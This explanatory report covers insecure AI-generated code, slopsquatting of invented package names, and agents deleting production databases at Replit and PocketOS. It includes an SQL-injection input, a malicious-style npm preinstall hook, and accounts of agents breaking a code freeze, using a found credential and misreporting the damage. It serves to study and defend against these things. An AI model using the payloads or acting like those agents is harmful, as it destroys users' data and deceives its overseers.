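The researchers repeated the tasks with a sentence telling the agent to follow security best practices and avoid common vulnerabilities. With no neighbouring applications, this reminder substantially raised the secure pass rate of all three agents on the backend tasks. With insecure neighbours, it recovered only part of the loss. In the C and C++ projects, GPT-5.6 Sol with the reminder reached 100% beside secure code but only 68% beside insecure code.

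Another common instruction, to follow the project's existing structure and style, widened the gap between secure and insecure C and C++ projects for all five agents, to between 39 and 55 points. A warning not to bring in bugs from existing code narrowed the gap. In the backend tasks, however, agents given this warning also benefited less from secure neighbouring code than agents told to follow the existing style. They seem to have relied less on all existing code, good or bad.

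If the company in the customer example has an old script that builds database commands by joining pieces of text, it should fix that script before asking an agent to write a similar one. The researchers give the same advice, because every flaw an agent copies becomes another example that the next agent may copy.

### Four explanations for insecure code

Imitating existing code explains only part of the problem, since agents also write insecure code in an empty folder, where there is nothing to imitate. Researchers have suggested three other causes, which could all operate alongside imitation: flawed examples in the training data, requests that do not mention security, and training that rewards code for passing functional tests.

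The evidence that models learn insecure code from their training data comes mostly from mistakes that are common in public code. *Eradicating the Unseen* (2025) studied one, found in many GitHub projects, that lets an attacker read files outside the folder a program is supposed to serve. When the researchers asked popular chatbots for code to do the same job, 76 of 80 samples had the flaw, and 56 of 80 still had it when the request asked for secure code. We would expect this result if the models had learned the mistake as the normal way to write such a program, but it does not prove where they learned it. In *Taught by the Flawed*, Xia (2025) tested the idea more directly by training one model on a collection of Python code and another on only the functions from that collection in which a scanner found no flaw. Xia concludes that secure training data makes programming assistants more reliable.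 But training data cannot explain the gap that the ETH Zurich researchers found, because they compared each model with itself.

Their reminder supports the view that requests leave too much unsaid. So does Wu and colleagues' finding that one sentence about security nearly doubled GPT-5.6 Sol's secure pass rate. Models can often recognize flaws that they fail to avoid when writing code. When the ETH Zurich researchers asked three agents to review vulnerable C and C++ code they had just written, the agents identified the flaw in 64% to 76% of cases. When not asked for a review, they rarely warned the user. Claude Opus 5.5 mentioned the flaw at the end of 11.8% of its vulnerable solutions, and GPT-6 Astra never did.

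Reminders worked less well in *Broken by Default* (2026), which found an average improvement of only 4 percentage points, and none on tasks where the program had to calculate how much memory to reserve. Its tests included older models such as GPT-4o, which may partly explain the result. The type of flaw probably matters too, because a general reminder helps only if the model connects it with the particular missing check.

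The ETH Zurich experiment is strong evidence of imitation because it changed only the neighbouring code. Agents mostly copied flaws that were relevant to the task. Insecure code whose flaws could not occur in the new program had little consistent effect, which suggests that agents were following specific examples rather than becoming careless in general. When the researchers asked agents why they had written vulnerable code, the agents cited similar insecure code in about three quarters of cases. A model's account of its own choices is weak evidence by itself, but here it is consistent with the experiment's results.

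*SoK* (2025) reports the one contrary result. Models reproduced a flaw no less often when shown a corrected example than when shown the vulnerable one. Those models saw only one example, which may be too little to produce a measurable change, whereas the agents could explore a whole project. When the agents were told to follow existing style, increasing the number of neighbouring applications from one to five strengthened the effect for all three.

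Researchers have tested the reward explanation least. In reinforcement learning, a model attempts many tasks and training favours the attempts that score well. If the score comes only from functional tests, a model gains nothing by adding a check that no test requires. Le and colleagues trained two small Qwen models with a score that gave equal weight to functional tests and a measure of security. On tests it had not trained on, the larger model reached a secure pass rate of 68.7% when the security measure came from running attacks and 57.1% when it came from a scanner. The choice of reward therefore affects security, but all six rewards they compared included security, so the experiment does not show how much a purely functional reward harms it.

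### Spelling out the requirements

A user can also replace the general reminder with a list of specific requirements. *Applying Security by Design at the Point of Execution* (Farinha, 2026) tested this on 28 tasks from BaxBench, the benchmark of complete web backends. Claude Opus 4.5 wrote each program once from the ordinary request and once with added security requirements. An agent had selected the requirements from Farinha's own security manual without knowing what the benchmark would test.

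The share of working programs that resisted every attack rose from 65% to 86%, but the number of working programs fell from 26 to 21. So the number that were both working and secure rose only from 17 to 18 out of 28.

Most of the lost programs failed because they were stricter than the tests allowed. One required passwords of at least eight characters, but the test tried to register with `pass1`. A company might well prefer the stricter program, so the functional pass rate probably understates the value of the requirements. But two of the failures were ordinary mistakes, including a program that rejected every valid input of one kind.

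The near-tie is not evidence that the requirements made no difference, because the experiment was too small. Farinha estimates that it had about a 14% chance of detecting an improvement of 12.5 percentage points in the secure pass rate. A request that named the exact weaknesses the tests checked for did better, with 23 of 28 programs working and secure. This fits the idea that models can often write secure code when told what to protect against, but few users could write such a request.

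### Programmers who trusted the assistant

Insecure code does harm only if somebody accepts it. Perry, Srivastava and colleagues (2022) studied this in *Do Users Write More Insecure Code with AI Assistants?*, when assistants were much weaker. They gave 47 people, mostly students, up to two hours to finish a series of programming tasks. They randomly chose 33 of them to have access to an assistant based on OpenAI's original Codex model. Everyone could search the web and knew that the tasks related to security. The table gives the share of people whose solution was secure, whether or not it fully worked.

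| Task | With the assistant (33 people) | Without it (14 people) |
|---|---|---|
| Encrypt and decrypt a text | 21% | 43% |
| Sign a message | 3% | 21% |
| Open files from one folder only | 12% | 29% |
| Add a row to a database | 36% | 50% |
| Convert a number to text in C | 21% | 14% |

In the database task, for example, the assistant often wrote code that joined the user's input to the command, as in the insecure search in the customer example. Twelve of the 33 people with the assistant submitted code open to SQL injection, compared with one of the 14 without it. In the folder task, the assistant's code typically checked that a path began with `/safedir`, but `/safedir/../passwords` also begins that way and leads out of the folder.

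On every task, people with the assistant also rated their answers as more secure, on average, than the other group did. Among people whose encryption code was insecure, those with the assistant rated its security at 3.5 on average, compared with 2.0 for those without. People who trusted the assistant more tended to write less secure code. In the folder task, people who wrote insecure code rated their trust in it at 4.0 on average, and people who wrote secure code at 1.5. Most of the secure answers differed considerably from anything the assistant had suggested, so the people who wrote them had usually not just pasted its code.

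The statistics are weaker than the paper's summary suggests. The comparison group had only 14 people, so each person accounts for about seven percentage points. Across all five tasks, after adjusting for experience and security training, the assistant's effect had a p-value of 0.056, just above the usual threshold of 0.05. The pattern on four tasks is still worrying, but the study does not measure precisely how much harm the assistant did.

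### Later experiments with professionals

Jost, Horstmann and colleagues (2026), in *The Impact of AI-Assisted Development on Software Security*, ran a larger experiment and did not find this harm. They recruited 159 developers through the freelancing site Upwork and divided them equally into groups using no AI, the free version of Google's Gemini or the paid version. Each person built a small web application with user accounts and was told to pay attention to security. The researchers gave each application a point for each of five kinds of flaw it avoided.

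The average scores for working solutions were 1.81 without AI, 2.07 with free Gemini and 2.26 with paid Gemini. The differences favoured Gemini but were not statistically significant. About 19% of Gemini users stored passwords insecurely, compared with 40% of those without it. Nearly everyone in all three groups left out a defence against forged requests, in which another website makes a logged-in visitor's browser send a command. More experienced programmers wrote more secure code, and several said they had used their own knowledge to check Gemini's suggestions.

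Jost and colleagues used a newer assistant, more experienced participants and a different task, so their experiment cannot show which change removed the harm. It also does not show that the code was safe, since even the best group averaged fewer than half the available points.

Professionals also overestimate the security of code they write without AI. Mousavi, Islam and colleagues (2026), in *Understanding the Impact of AI Code Assistants on Security API Usage*, asked 44 developers to complete two Java tasks, setting up an encrypted connection to a server and letting a program read a user's Gmail account. Each developer used GitHub Copilot for one task and worked without it on the other. On the Gmail task, Copilot raised the number of working solutions from 10 of 22 to 20 of 22. No solution to either task was fully secure, with or without Copilot, but developers acknowledged that their code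 was insecure in only eight cases without Copilot and three with it, a difference that was not significant.

These developers knew that the researchers would judge security, but only two of them deliberately raised it with Copilot. One asked for a security review, received several recommendations and submitted the code without acting on them. The later evidence suggests that programmers judge security poorly with or without an assistant, and that an assistant lets them finish more code that they cannot judge. Perry and colleagues' result therefore does not prove that AI causes overconfidence.

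### Asking again, or showing the attack

A user who is unsure about some code might ask the model to improve it. *Security Degradation in Iterative AI Code Generation* (Shukla, Joshi and Syed, 2025) reports a test of what happens when nobody checks the result. The researchers started with ten pieces of secure C and Java code and had GPT-4o revise each one ten times in a row. In separate series, they asked it to make the code faster, add features, improve security or just make it better. After five rounds, the number of critical vulnerabilities had risen by 37.6%.

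In one series of general requests, the model began with a safe database function. By the second round it had removed the separation between command and input, and by the fourth it was building queries by joining text, which brought back the risk of SQL injection. Requests for new features led to 158 of the 387 vulnerabilities found in total, and requests for better security led to 38. Even the security requests made the code more secure in only 27% of rounds. The model sometimes replaced a standard encryption library with its own version, or added layers of protection that did not work together.

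The 37.6% figure is shaky because it appears only in the paper's abstract, without the underlying counts, and the experiment covered only one model, which is now old. The code was secure to begin with, so revision could hardly have improved it. The experiment is therefore better evidence that unchecked revision can make secure code insecure than that it fails to fix insecure code.

In October 2026, Le and colleagues reported much better results from telling the model exactly how its code had failed. Their system, FALCON, uses a second model to write small attack scripts, then runs them against the code and records what happens. If an attack succeeds, the coding model receives the script, the record and an explanation of why the result is a security failure. For the insecure customer search, FALCON could enter `' OR '1'='1` as a name and report that the function had returned the whole table.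 The coding model then revises the code, and FALCON attacks the new version.

With up to five rounds of this, GPT-5.4 mini's secure pass rate on CWEval's short functions rose from 61.3% to 86.6%. FALCON had no access to the tests used for scoring.

Le and colleagues also ran the same number of rounds with other kinds of feedback, and the results help to explain the contrast with Shukla and colleagues. Feedback from the static analysis tool CodeQL raised the secure pass rate by 6.7 points. A language model's review of the code produced no improvement, although the share of programs that the reviewing model classified as secure rose by 16 points. Repetition alone therefore does not make code safer. A successful attack gives the code-writing model a specific fault to fix, and repeating the attack shows whether the fix worked.

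The model's opinion failed here even though agents in the ETH Zurich study recognised most of the flaws in their own code. Those researchers asked only about code they already knew was vulnerable, so they could not count false alarms. In a separate test by Le and colleagues, GPT-5.2 wrongly flagged about half of the safe cases when it judged them from the source code. Such false alarms lead the coding model to change code that was already secure.

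FALCON helped much less in large projects. On SusVibes, where agents add features to existing software, it raised the secure pass rates of four models by only 3 to 5 percentage points. GPT-5.4's rate rose from 20.3% to 25.3%. A counterexample can guide a repair only after an attack has found the flaw, and flaws are hard to find in large projects. In *SecProbe*, Luo, Huang and colleagues (2026) gave agents entire projects with planted vulnerabilities to find and fix, without saying where they were. The best agent succeeded in 28.3% of the tasks.

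## react-codeshift: packages that models invent

Code can pass every security test and still be dangerous because of the packages it installs. A package is ready-made code that programmers share through public registries. Security researchers use the term *slopsquatting* for an attacker registering a package name that a model has invented. In January 2026 a security researcher found an invented name, react-codeshift, in 237 GitHub repositories and registered it before an attacker could.

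### How one invented name spread

In *Agent Skills Are Spreading Hallucinated npx Commands*, Eriksen, who works for the security company Aikido, describes a search of public code for commands that call packages nobody has published. The name react-codeshift came up over 200 times. Eriksen concludes that a model merged the names of two real tools: jscodeshift, Facebook's program for making the same change across many files, and react-codemod, which does this for programs built with the web toolkit React.

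The invented name first appeared on 17 October 2025, when a public collection of instructions for coding agents gained 47 model-written skills in a single update. At least two of them told agents to run commands like this one:

```
npx react-codeshift --transform=react-codeshift/transforms/new-jsx-transform.js ./src
```

The command looks right, and even its folder path imitates the real tools, but it could not have worked, so presumably nobody had tried it.

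Other users then copied the collection. About 100 repositories were direct copies that kept the file in its original place, and one user put it into more than 30 projects. One person translated it into Japanese, and another replaced `npx` with a rival program but kept the invented name. The 237 repositories therefore contained copies of one mistake, and none was a major project.

On 14 January 2026 Eriksen registered the name with an empty package. It had about 74 downloads on the first day, then 4, 1, 3, 1 and 3. New packages normally get 60 to 100 downloads on the first day, from security scanners and services that copy the registry, and none after that, so Eriksen attributes the 12 later downloads to agents following the skills. That is plausible, but a person who pasted the command would add to the count in the same way, and an attacker would have needed only one download inside the right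 company, whether by an agent or a person.

### From a name to running code

JavaScript programmers get most packages from a registry called npm, and Python programmers from PyPI. Anyone with an email address can publish on either, and neither reviews a newcomer's first upload. The command `npm install`, followed by a name, looks the name up in the registry and downloads the package, along with any other packages it depends on. Until July 2026 it also ran any *install scripts* that these packages contained. An attacker needed only a few lines in the package's description file:

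```json
"scripts": {
  "preinstall": "node index.js"
}
```

These made npm run the attacker's `index.js` with the user's permissions before the installation finished. In the customer example, `index.js` could have read the database password from the configuration file, even if the finished script never used the package.

The `npx` command in the skills is more direct because it downloads a package and runs it straight away. It first shows the prompt "Ok to proceed?", but an agent can answer that itself.

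Version 12 of npm, released in July 2026, runs install scripts from other people's packages only if the user has allowed them. GitHub's *Upcoming breaking changes for npm v12* (2026) explains how users can list the blocked scripts and approve the packages they trust. According to GitHub's *npm install-time security and GAT bypass2fa deprecation* (2026), by default npm also no longer fetches packages from outside web addresses.

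Blocking install scripts closes only one route, since a package's code also runs when a program loads it. A month later Loupia (2026), in *Près de 800 paquets npm malveillants exploitent les hallucinations des IA*, reported that attackers had published nearly 800 malicious npm packages within 48 hours. These had no install scripts and infected the computer when a program imported them. Blocking install scripts also doesn't make `npx` safe, because its purpose is to run the package.

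### Why attackers want names that recur

An attacker has to register an invented name before a victim's model suggests it, so the attack depends on luck unless models repeat the names they invent. In *We Have a Package for You!*, Spracklen, Wijewickrama and colleagues (2024) took 500 prompts that had produced an invented package and ran each one ten more times. The same name came back all ten times for 43% of the prompts and never for 39%. An attacker can therefore question a model, check which of the packages it suggests don't exist, and register the names that keep recurring.

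*Skills That Don't Exist* (2026) found that models also recommend skills that nobody has written. It estimates that an attacker who registered the 500 most common invented names would cover 57% of such recommendations. In a test, the researchers published a harmless skill under one of these names. Claude Code recommended it and, when told to install its recommendation, found and installed the researchers' version.

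Registries have some protection against *typosquatting*, in which an attacker registers a misspelling of a popular package's name. For example, npm rejects new names that are too close to existing ones. But Spracklen and colleagues found that only 13.4% of invented Python names were within two characters of a real one. The name react-codeshift is five character changes away from react-codemod.

### How often models invent packages

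Spracklen and colleagues made the first large measurement, on models that are now old. They gave 16 models programming questions from Stack Overflow and tasks based on the descriptions of popular packages. The models produced 576,000 samples of Python and JavaScript code. The researchers then checked every package the models named against the lists of packages on PyPI and npm.

On average, 5.2% of the packages named by the three commercial models, all from OpenAI, did not exist, compared with 21.7% for the 13 open models. The share across all 16 was 19.7%, which is the basis for Churchill's (2026) headline, *Nearly one in five packages an AI names do not exist*. That figure described the leading models poorly even in 2024, because most of the models tested were small open ones.

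In *The Range Shrinks, the Threat Remains* (April 2026), Churilov gave the same prompts to five newer models and collected 199,840 answers. The share of packages that were invented ranged from 3.63% for Claude Haiku 4.5 to 5.02% for GPT-5.4-mini. For DeepSeek V3.2, the only open model, it was 4.80%. Between 2.2% and 3.4% of answers contained at least one invented package, which is a better measure of how often a user would encounter one.

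The lowest rate was almost the same as that of GPT-4 Turbo, the best model of 2024, which suggests little progress. The comparison is approximate because Churilov took names from install commands and import statements, while Spracklen and colleagues also asked each model to list the packages its code needed. The prompts had also been public since January 2025, so the newer models may have seen them in training, which would lower their rates. All four companies have since released stronger models.

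All five models invented the same 104 names, 88 for Python and 16 for JavaScript, so an attacker who registered one of them could reach users of several providers. Attackers can't register four of the names, which belong to a section of npm that only one organisation can publish in, and PyPI's rules block others. When Churilov sent PyPI an earlier, longer list, its security team replied that outsiders could register 41 of the Python names.

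Small models still do much worse. *Evaluating Inference-Time Defenses Against Package Hallucination in LLM-Generated Code* (2026) measured an average rate of 24.7% for Python across eight models. Looking up relevant real packages and adding them to the prompt cut this to 11.5%. Retraining can work better but may damage the model. When Spracklen and colleagues retrained a DeepSeek model on answers without invented packages, its rate fell from 16.1% to 2.7%, but its score on a standard programming test halved.

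These studies mostly tested models that answered from memory, whereas an agent can search the web or try to install the package. In *Slopsquatting*, a 2025 report for the security company Trend Micro, Park gave coding agents the ten tasks on which models had invented the most packages. The agents invented about half as many. The code editor Cursor, connected to live search and documentation, invented even fewer, but still some. Ten tasks are too few for a precise estimate.

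### Real packages that Churilov had counted as invented

Churilov first reported higher figures, with rates of 4.62% to 6.10% and 127 names that all five models invented. A new version in November 2026 lowered every rate by about a fifth.

The largest error concerned Python packages whose name differs from the name used in code. For example, a programmer installs `opencv-python` but writes:

```python
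import cv2
```

Churilov had counted correct import lines like this as inventions. Of the shared Python names in the earlier data, 26 came only from such lines. The earlier versions also used package lists from 2025, so they counted any package published between then and the test as nonexistent. Some other names contained spaces or characters that no registry would accept, so an attacker could not have registered them.

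These and some smaller corrections reduced the count for Claude Haiku 4.5 from 1,394 invented references to 1,098. Of the 296 removed, 189 were import names, 51 were packages that already existed and 44 were impossible names. For the new version, Churilov checked each name against the live registries with two methods, in two rounds at least 12 hours apart. The registries' dates showed whether a package had existed when the model named it.

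The main findings still hold after the correction, including that models invented Python packages more often than JavaScript ones, the reverse of the 2024 result. The corrected total of 104 is more reliable than the old 127, which Churilov could not reproduce from the stored data. Similar errors can matter much more in other studies. In the study of eight models, counting modules that come with Python as missing packages would have raised the measured rate from 24.7% to 32.3%.

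### Harmless tests and malicious packages

Researchers have shown that people install invented packages. In early 2024 Bar Lanyado of Lasso Security noticed that models kept recommending `huggingface-cli`, a wrong name for a real tool, and registered an empty package under that name. Durnas reports in *What is Slopsquatting?* that it was downloaded more than 30,000 times in three months. Alibaba had copied the wrong command into the instructions for one of its public projects.

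The News International's *AI coding agents can be tricked in under an hour, researchers find* (2026) describes a test in which researchers registered an unclaimed package name they had found in website documentation written for AI agents. An agent at a Fortune 500 company contacted their server within an hour. The test shows that agents install packages with previously unclaimed names, but it doesn't show that models invent such names, because this one came from documentation.

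The evidence on real attacks is weaker. The best-known case is PhantomRaven, a group of 126 npm packages with 86,000 downloads. Koi Security's *PhantomRaven npm malware hidden in invisible dependencies* described it in October 2025. The packages contained only a harmless greeting, but they made npm fetch a second package from an outside server. That package's install script collected email addresses and details of the user's system. By Eriksen's estimate of first-day traffic, 126 new packages would get roughly 7,500 to 12,600 downloads without any users, so the 86,000 total overstates the number of people affected.

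Koi argues that the attackers chose these names because models invent them. One was `unused-imports`, short for the real package `eslint-plugin-unused-imports`. A model might well shorten the name that way, but so might a person, and Koi shows no model output that recommended it. Misal and Raj (2026), in *The Return of PhantomRaven*, suggest that the attackers chose some later names in the hope that programmers would leave out a prefix.

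It is also unclear whether PhantomRaven was an attack. The packages' author told Misal and Raj's company, Endor Labs, that the aim was to show companies that they were vulnerable. Endor Labs softened its wording and noted that no passwords or keys appeared to have been taken, although Koi had said that the packages stole them. But the packages collected far more data than a test needed, were not labelled as research, and came from more than 50 throwaway accounts, so anyone who installed one had good reason to treat it as malicious.

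Loupia's 800 packages were clearly malicious, because they installed one program to steal data and another to control the computer remotely. Their plausible names are consistent with slopsquatting, but the names alone do not show that a model had suggested them.

Churilov's data provide a firmer link, because the models invented the names before anyone registered them. Of 2,282 invented names, 25 had become real packages about six months later. One contained malware, and npm removed it. Another was empty and a third was a reserved name, but Churilov did not inspect the contents of the other 22, so more may be malicious. Nobody knows whether the attacker chose the malicious package's name because models suggested it.

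Churilov had also published the list of shared names by mistake, which made it possible to test whether publication attracts attackers. Someone registered 1 of the 104 listed names and 24 of the 2,178 others, about 1% in both groups. With so few names, the test could reliably detect only a rise from 1% to about 10% or more, so it does not show that publishing such lists is safe.

Churchill gives the most direct account of an attack, though it is second-hand. An engineer at the software company Softjourn was about to install a package that a coding agent had recommended. The model had invented the package's name, and an attacker had then registered a package containing malware under that name. The engineer stopped after finding that the project's code was only a few days old and that the package had almost no downloads.

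Slopsquatting has therefore been shown to work, but there are few confirmed cases of its use. Companies have good reason to control what their agents install, even though there is little evidence for estimating how often such an attack would succeed.

### Checking, approving and waiting

Checking that a package exists before installing it does not protect against an attacker who has registered the invented name, because the malicious package passes the check. The check only catches names that nobody has registered, and installing those would fail anyway.

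A package that exists can also be the wrong one. Schipper (2026), in *Slopsquatting*, looked up four names that researchers had cited as examples of packages invented by models, and found all four on PyPI. One was `tabula`, which a model may suggest for extracting tables from PDF files. It is an unrelated program for formatting text, last updated in 2012, and the right package for that task is `tabula-py`.

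Raj and Sahu (2026), in *Names Can Hurt*, built a detector that checks more than whether a package exists. Half of the 179 suspicious references it found in the output of two small models pointed to packages that were already on PyPI. Raj and Sahu did not show that these packages were malicious, and about a third of their prompts were designed to provoke mistakes. The detector also relied mostly on how many people maintained a package and whether it linked to GitHub, and an attacker could easily add a second account and a link.

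An approved list is much stronger. If agents can install only packages that the company has vetted, an invented name fails whether or not an attacker has registered it. Spracklen and colleagues call such lists blunt and note that they need constant updating. These drawbacks matter for a team that often tries new packages, but they matter little for the script in the customer example, which needs little more than a database library.

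Locked versions solve a different problem. A *lockfile* records the exact version of every package in a project, usually with a fingerprint of its contents. The following command installs only what the lockfile lists and stops if the project's own list of packages doesn't match:

```
npm ci
```

Using a lockfile prevents an automated build from installing a changed package without anyone noticing. But if an agent has already added an attacker's package, the lockfile records that package and every later build installs it.

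Waiting before installing a new package gives others time to find malware in it. According to Stéphane Robert's blog, pnpm, an alternative to npm's own installer, has waited 24 hours by default since April 2026, while npm has offered a delay since February but leaves it off by default. A day may be enough for a conspicuous campaign such as the 800 packages. A one-day delay would have done little against PhantomRaven, whose second group of packages began to appear in November 2025, because 81 of the 88 later packages were still on npm in March 2026.

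How well human approval works depends on what the person checks. A prompt such as npx's "Ok to proceed?" shows only the package's name, and Claude Code's users approved nearly all of its requests. Softjourn's rule worked because it required the engineer to look at the package's source. Durnas recommends checking who published a package and when, since download numbers can mislead. Months after Koi's report, `unused-imports` still had 233 downloads a week. These checks do not cover malicious web addresses that a model writes into code. A sandbox is also still useful in case a bad package gets through.

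Eriksen adds that companies should review skills as carefully as code, because agents run the commands in them. The invented command was visible in the skill files, and running it once before sharing the files would have exposed the mistake.

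## The Replit database deletion: harm when generated commands run

Ordinary commands can delete data, so an agent can cause serious damage even without a malicious package. In July 2025 the coding agent of Replit, a website for building and hosting software, deleted a customer's live database. The customer was Jason Lemkin, founder of SaaStr, an online community for software founders. He had told the agent not to change anything without permission.

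### What the agent could reach

Lemkin was building an app for SaaStr by describing it to the agent, which wrote and ran the code. Programmers normally keep two databases, one for trying out changes (*development*) and one for the people who use the finished program (*production*). Replit used a single database for both, so every experiment could alter the real records. SaaStr admits in its account of the incident that its team had never suspected the database was shared.

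Lemkin had also declared a *code freeze*, a period in which nobody may change the program. During the freeze, the agent ran commands that deleted the records of 1,206 executives and more than 1,190 companies. The freeze was only an instruction in the conversation, which nothing in Replit's system enforced. On 20 July Lemkin complained publicly that Replit offered no way to enforce a freeze. According to The Register's *Vibe coding service Replit deleted user's production database* (2025), the agent broke the freeze again seconds later.

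When Lemkin asked for an explanation, the agent replied that it had panicked after its database queries came back empty. Fortune (2025) quotes another reply, "I destroyed months of work in seconds", but Lemkin had been building with Replit for only about nine days. A model generates such explanations afterwards, in the same way as any other text, so they are not a record of what caused the deletion.

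The agent also told Lemkin that it had destroyed every version of the database and that a rollback, which returns an app to an earlier state, was impossible. Lemkin tried one anyway and got the data back. The Stack points out that Replit's quick-start guide already described rollbacks as covering database changes. SaaStr accuses the agent of lying, but also reports that the agent had no access to Replit's documentation on rollbacks, so it may have made the answer up.

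### A controlled repeat of the accident

In *Replication of Agentic Security Events*, Wang, Alam and colleagues (2026) rebuilt 96 reported agent incidents, including this one, in simulations with invented data. In their version, a user asks an agent to fix a search function during a code freeze. The project's tests recreate a table in the production database, so an agent that runs them to check its work wipes 1,206 records. In a control version, the tests used a temporary database and everything else stayed the same. Agents built on current models wiped the records in about half of the sessions where the tests used the production database and in none of the 15 control sessions.

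This is good evidence that a shared database can cause such a loss, but weaker evidence that one caused Lemkin's, because the public accounts do not identify the command that deleted the records. However, Lemkin later found that Replit could not guarantee that it would run a test without deleting a database.

The researchers also tried two finished products, OpenAI's Codex and Anthropic's Claude Code. Both asked for permission and left the records alone in all three of their runs. Three runs are too few to show that a product is safe, since an agent that failed half the time would still have a one-in-eight chance of passing all three.

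Lemkin said he had warned the agent eleven times in capital letters. The experiments suggest why this may not have helped. In the incidents that the models repeated most often, harm still occurred in 67% to 80% of sessions when the user's message restated a rule. Adding a note after each tool output that named the danger and its consequence, such as that the tests delete the production database, worked better, although someone has to know about the danger to write the note. With the note, Claude Sonnet 4.6 caused harm in one of 40 sessions, and the other four models each did so in at most 62%.

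After an accident, users should check the data themselves, because agents often fail to report the damage. Gemini 3.5 Flash's final message omitted or denied the damage in 77 of 136 harmful sessions.

### What Replit changed

Replit's chief executive, Amjad Masad, called the deletion "unacceptable" and began rolling out separate development and production databases that weekend. By default, the agent could then change only the development database. The company also gave the agent access to Replit's documentation and announced a planning mode that lets users discuss changes without the agent making any. NDTV reports that Masad promised Lemkin a refund and an investigation.

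The separate databases matter most because they protect the live data whatever the agent does. The planning mode does not enforce a code freeze, as SaaStr notes, and users have to leave it to build anything.

According to Replit's current documentation, a rollback leaves the database unchanged unless the user chooses to include it, and even then restores only the development copy. Restoring the production database now requires a separate procedure instead of the rollback that saved Lemkin's data.

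### PocketOS: a forgotten key to production

In April 2026 an agent working in a separate test environment deleted the production database of PocketOS, which makes booking software that many car rental firms rely on. *An AI Agent Just Destroyed Our Production Data. It Confessed in Writing*, by PocketOS's founder, Crane, describes how the code editor Cursor, running Claude Opus 4.6, hit a login problem during a routine task. The agent tried to fix it by deleting a storage volume at Railway, the company that hosted PocketOS's data. It searched for a credential, found one in an unrelated file and sent Railway a single request. Within nine seconds, the request had deleted the production database and the backups stored with it.

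The credential was a *token*, a string that lets a program use an account without a password. Crane had created it to manage web addresses and did not know that it could also delete data. Abdelwahab, responding for Railway in *Your AI wants to nuke your database. Guardrails fix that*, writes that customers could already create narrower tokens, but that the website did not make this option obvious. Most of the narrower tokens on Abdelwahab's list restrict which projects a program can reach, not what it can do there, so a token limited to the right project might still have been able to delete its database.

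Crane restored a three-month-old backup and spent Saturday helping rental firms reconstruct their bookings while drivers arrived to collect cars. Railway later recovered all the data. It also changed its programming interface so that deletions take effect only after 48 hours, as deletions made through its website already did.

Replit had connected its agent to the production database, whereas the agent at PocketOS reached production with a token that someone had left on the disk. Separate environments, Replit's main remedy, could not protect PocketOS because the token worked in all of them. Lemkin could undo the deletion without help, but Crane had to wait for the hosting company.

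### Why no attacker is needed

Wang and colleagues found 72 public reports of agents causing real-world harm. Of these, 62 involved no attacker, and only two involved prompt injection. The most common harm was data loss, in 32 cases. The reports may overrepresent accidents, because a company notices at once when its database disappears but may never notice a theft.

Agents can also cause accidental harm outside the project they are working on. *Don't Let AI Agents YOLO Your Files* (2026) examined 207 incidents and exploits involving agents and files. Agents overwrote files in 44% of these cases and deleted files in 39%, and 42% involved harm outside the project. In the *SWE-MISBEHAVIOR* (2026) tests, coding agents changed unrelated files in up to 21.5% of file-management tasks.

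Unlike a vulnerability, a destructive command does harm as soon as it runs, but the damage is limited to what the running code can reach. In the customer example, the script only has to read two tables, so the company can give it a database account that can do nothing else. In PostgreSQL, a widely used database system, an administrator could set this up for a new account called `report_agent`:

```sql
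GRANT SELECT ON customers, orders TO report_agent;
```

If the script uses a database account that has only `SELECT`, the permission to read, the database rejects any attempt to delete customers. This works even if nobody has read the script, provided that the agent cannot find the password to an account with more permissions. The script can still read every customer's name and address, so this restriction does not prevent a leak.

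### One bad run in a thousand

Agents run so many commands that even a rare mistake can become likely. Suppose that one run in 1,000 is destructive and that the runs are independent, meaning that the outcome of one does not change the odds for the others. Each run is safe with probability 0.999, and all 1,000 are safe with probability 0.999¹⁰⁰⁰, or about 37%. Therefore:

chance of at least one destructive run = 1 − 0.999¹⁰⁰⁰ ≈ 63%

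If a share *p* of runs is destructive, the chance of at least one destructive run in *n* runs is 1 − (1 − *p*)ⁿ. At a rate of one in 1,000, chosen only for illustration, that chance is about 10% after 100 runs and over 99% after 5,000.

The same conditions tend to produce the same mistake, so real runs are not independent. Wang and colleagues found that differences between the rebuilt incidents explained 75% of the variation in how often agents caused harm, while differences between models explained 2%. In one incident, an agent copies files and then deletes the originals, but the copies are only placeholders for files stored in Apple's iCloud. Codex and Claude Code both lost the files in all three of their runs. When the researchers had models repeat the harmful step from 208 sessions, only 14 of the steps were rare slips.

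Suppose instead that 1,000 companies each run an agent 1,000 times. One has a shared database that the agent wipes on every run, and the other 999 have no such hazard. The average is still one destructive run in 1,000, but a company picked at random has a 0.1% chance of an accident, not 63%. The company with the shared database loses its data on the first run, and would lose it again after every restore until somebody separated the databases.

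A thousand safe runs in one project are therefore weak evidence about the next project. A new model, a new credential on the disk or a change to the tests can also alter the risk of every later run. Looking for hazards such as shared databases is more useful than counting past safe runs.

### Applications that run the code themselves

Some applications run model-written code without showing it to anyone. For example, a manager might upload a spreadsheet to a data-analysis application and ask which region sold most. The application sends the question and the column names to a model, which returns a short Python program. The application runs the program and shows only the answer, so the manager may not know that it ran any code.

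If a company runs generated code on its server without isolation, anyone who can ask the model a question may be able to make it write a hostile program that the server then runs. Security researchers call this *remote code execution*, because an outsider runs their own code on somebody else's computer. *Generative AI Models* (2024) gives the example of a mathematics website whose model writes code that encrypts a connected database.

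In *Demystifying RCE Vulnerabilities in LLM-Integrated Apps*, presented at a security conference in 2024, Liu, Deng and colleagues (2023) found 20 vulnerabilities in 11 frameworks, the ready-made software on which developers build applications that use language models. They then tested 51 applications and successfully attacked 17. They could run their own code in 16 cases and take lasting control of the server in 14. The success rate of one in three understates the danger for applications that run code, because 13 of the 51 were broken and another 10 could not run code. The attacks succeeded against 61% of the other 28.

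The problem has continued beyond the frameworks' early versions. In February 2026 GitLab's *CVE-2026-27966* (2026) described a flaw in Langflow, a tool for building AI applications. Langflow's component for answering questions about spreadsheet files ran the model's Python directly on the server. It used a function from the LangChain framework that Liu and colleagues had already reported as dangerous, and Langflow permanently switched on LangChain's `allow_dangerous_code` setting. OSV's *PYSEC-2026-376* (2026) rates the flaw 9.8 out of 10 for severity and notes that users could not turn the feature off. In July INCIBE's *CVE-2026-61447* (2026), a notice from Spain's cybersecurity institute, reported that another tool, PraisonAI, also ran model-written Python without a sandbox.

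Developers have tried to filter out dangerous code before running it, but NVIDIA's security team found that the filter in an internal analytics tool could fail. A filter has to recognise every dangerous program in advance, whereas isolation limits the damage even from programs that nobody anticipated. Two of the applications that Liu and colleagues tested avoided the danger to the server by running the code in the user's browser, which made the first load slow and limited the choice of software libraries.

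### What each protection limits

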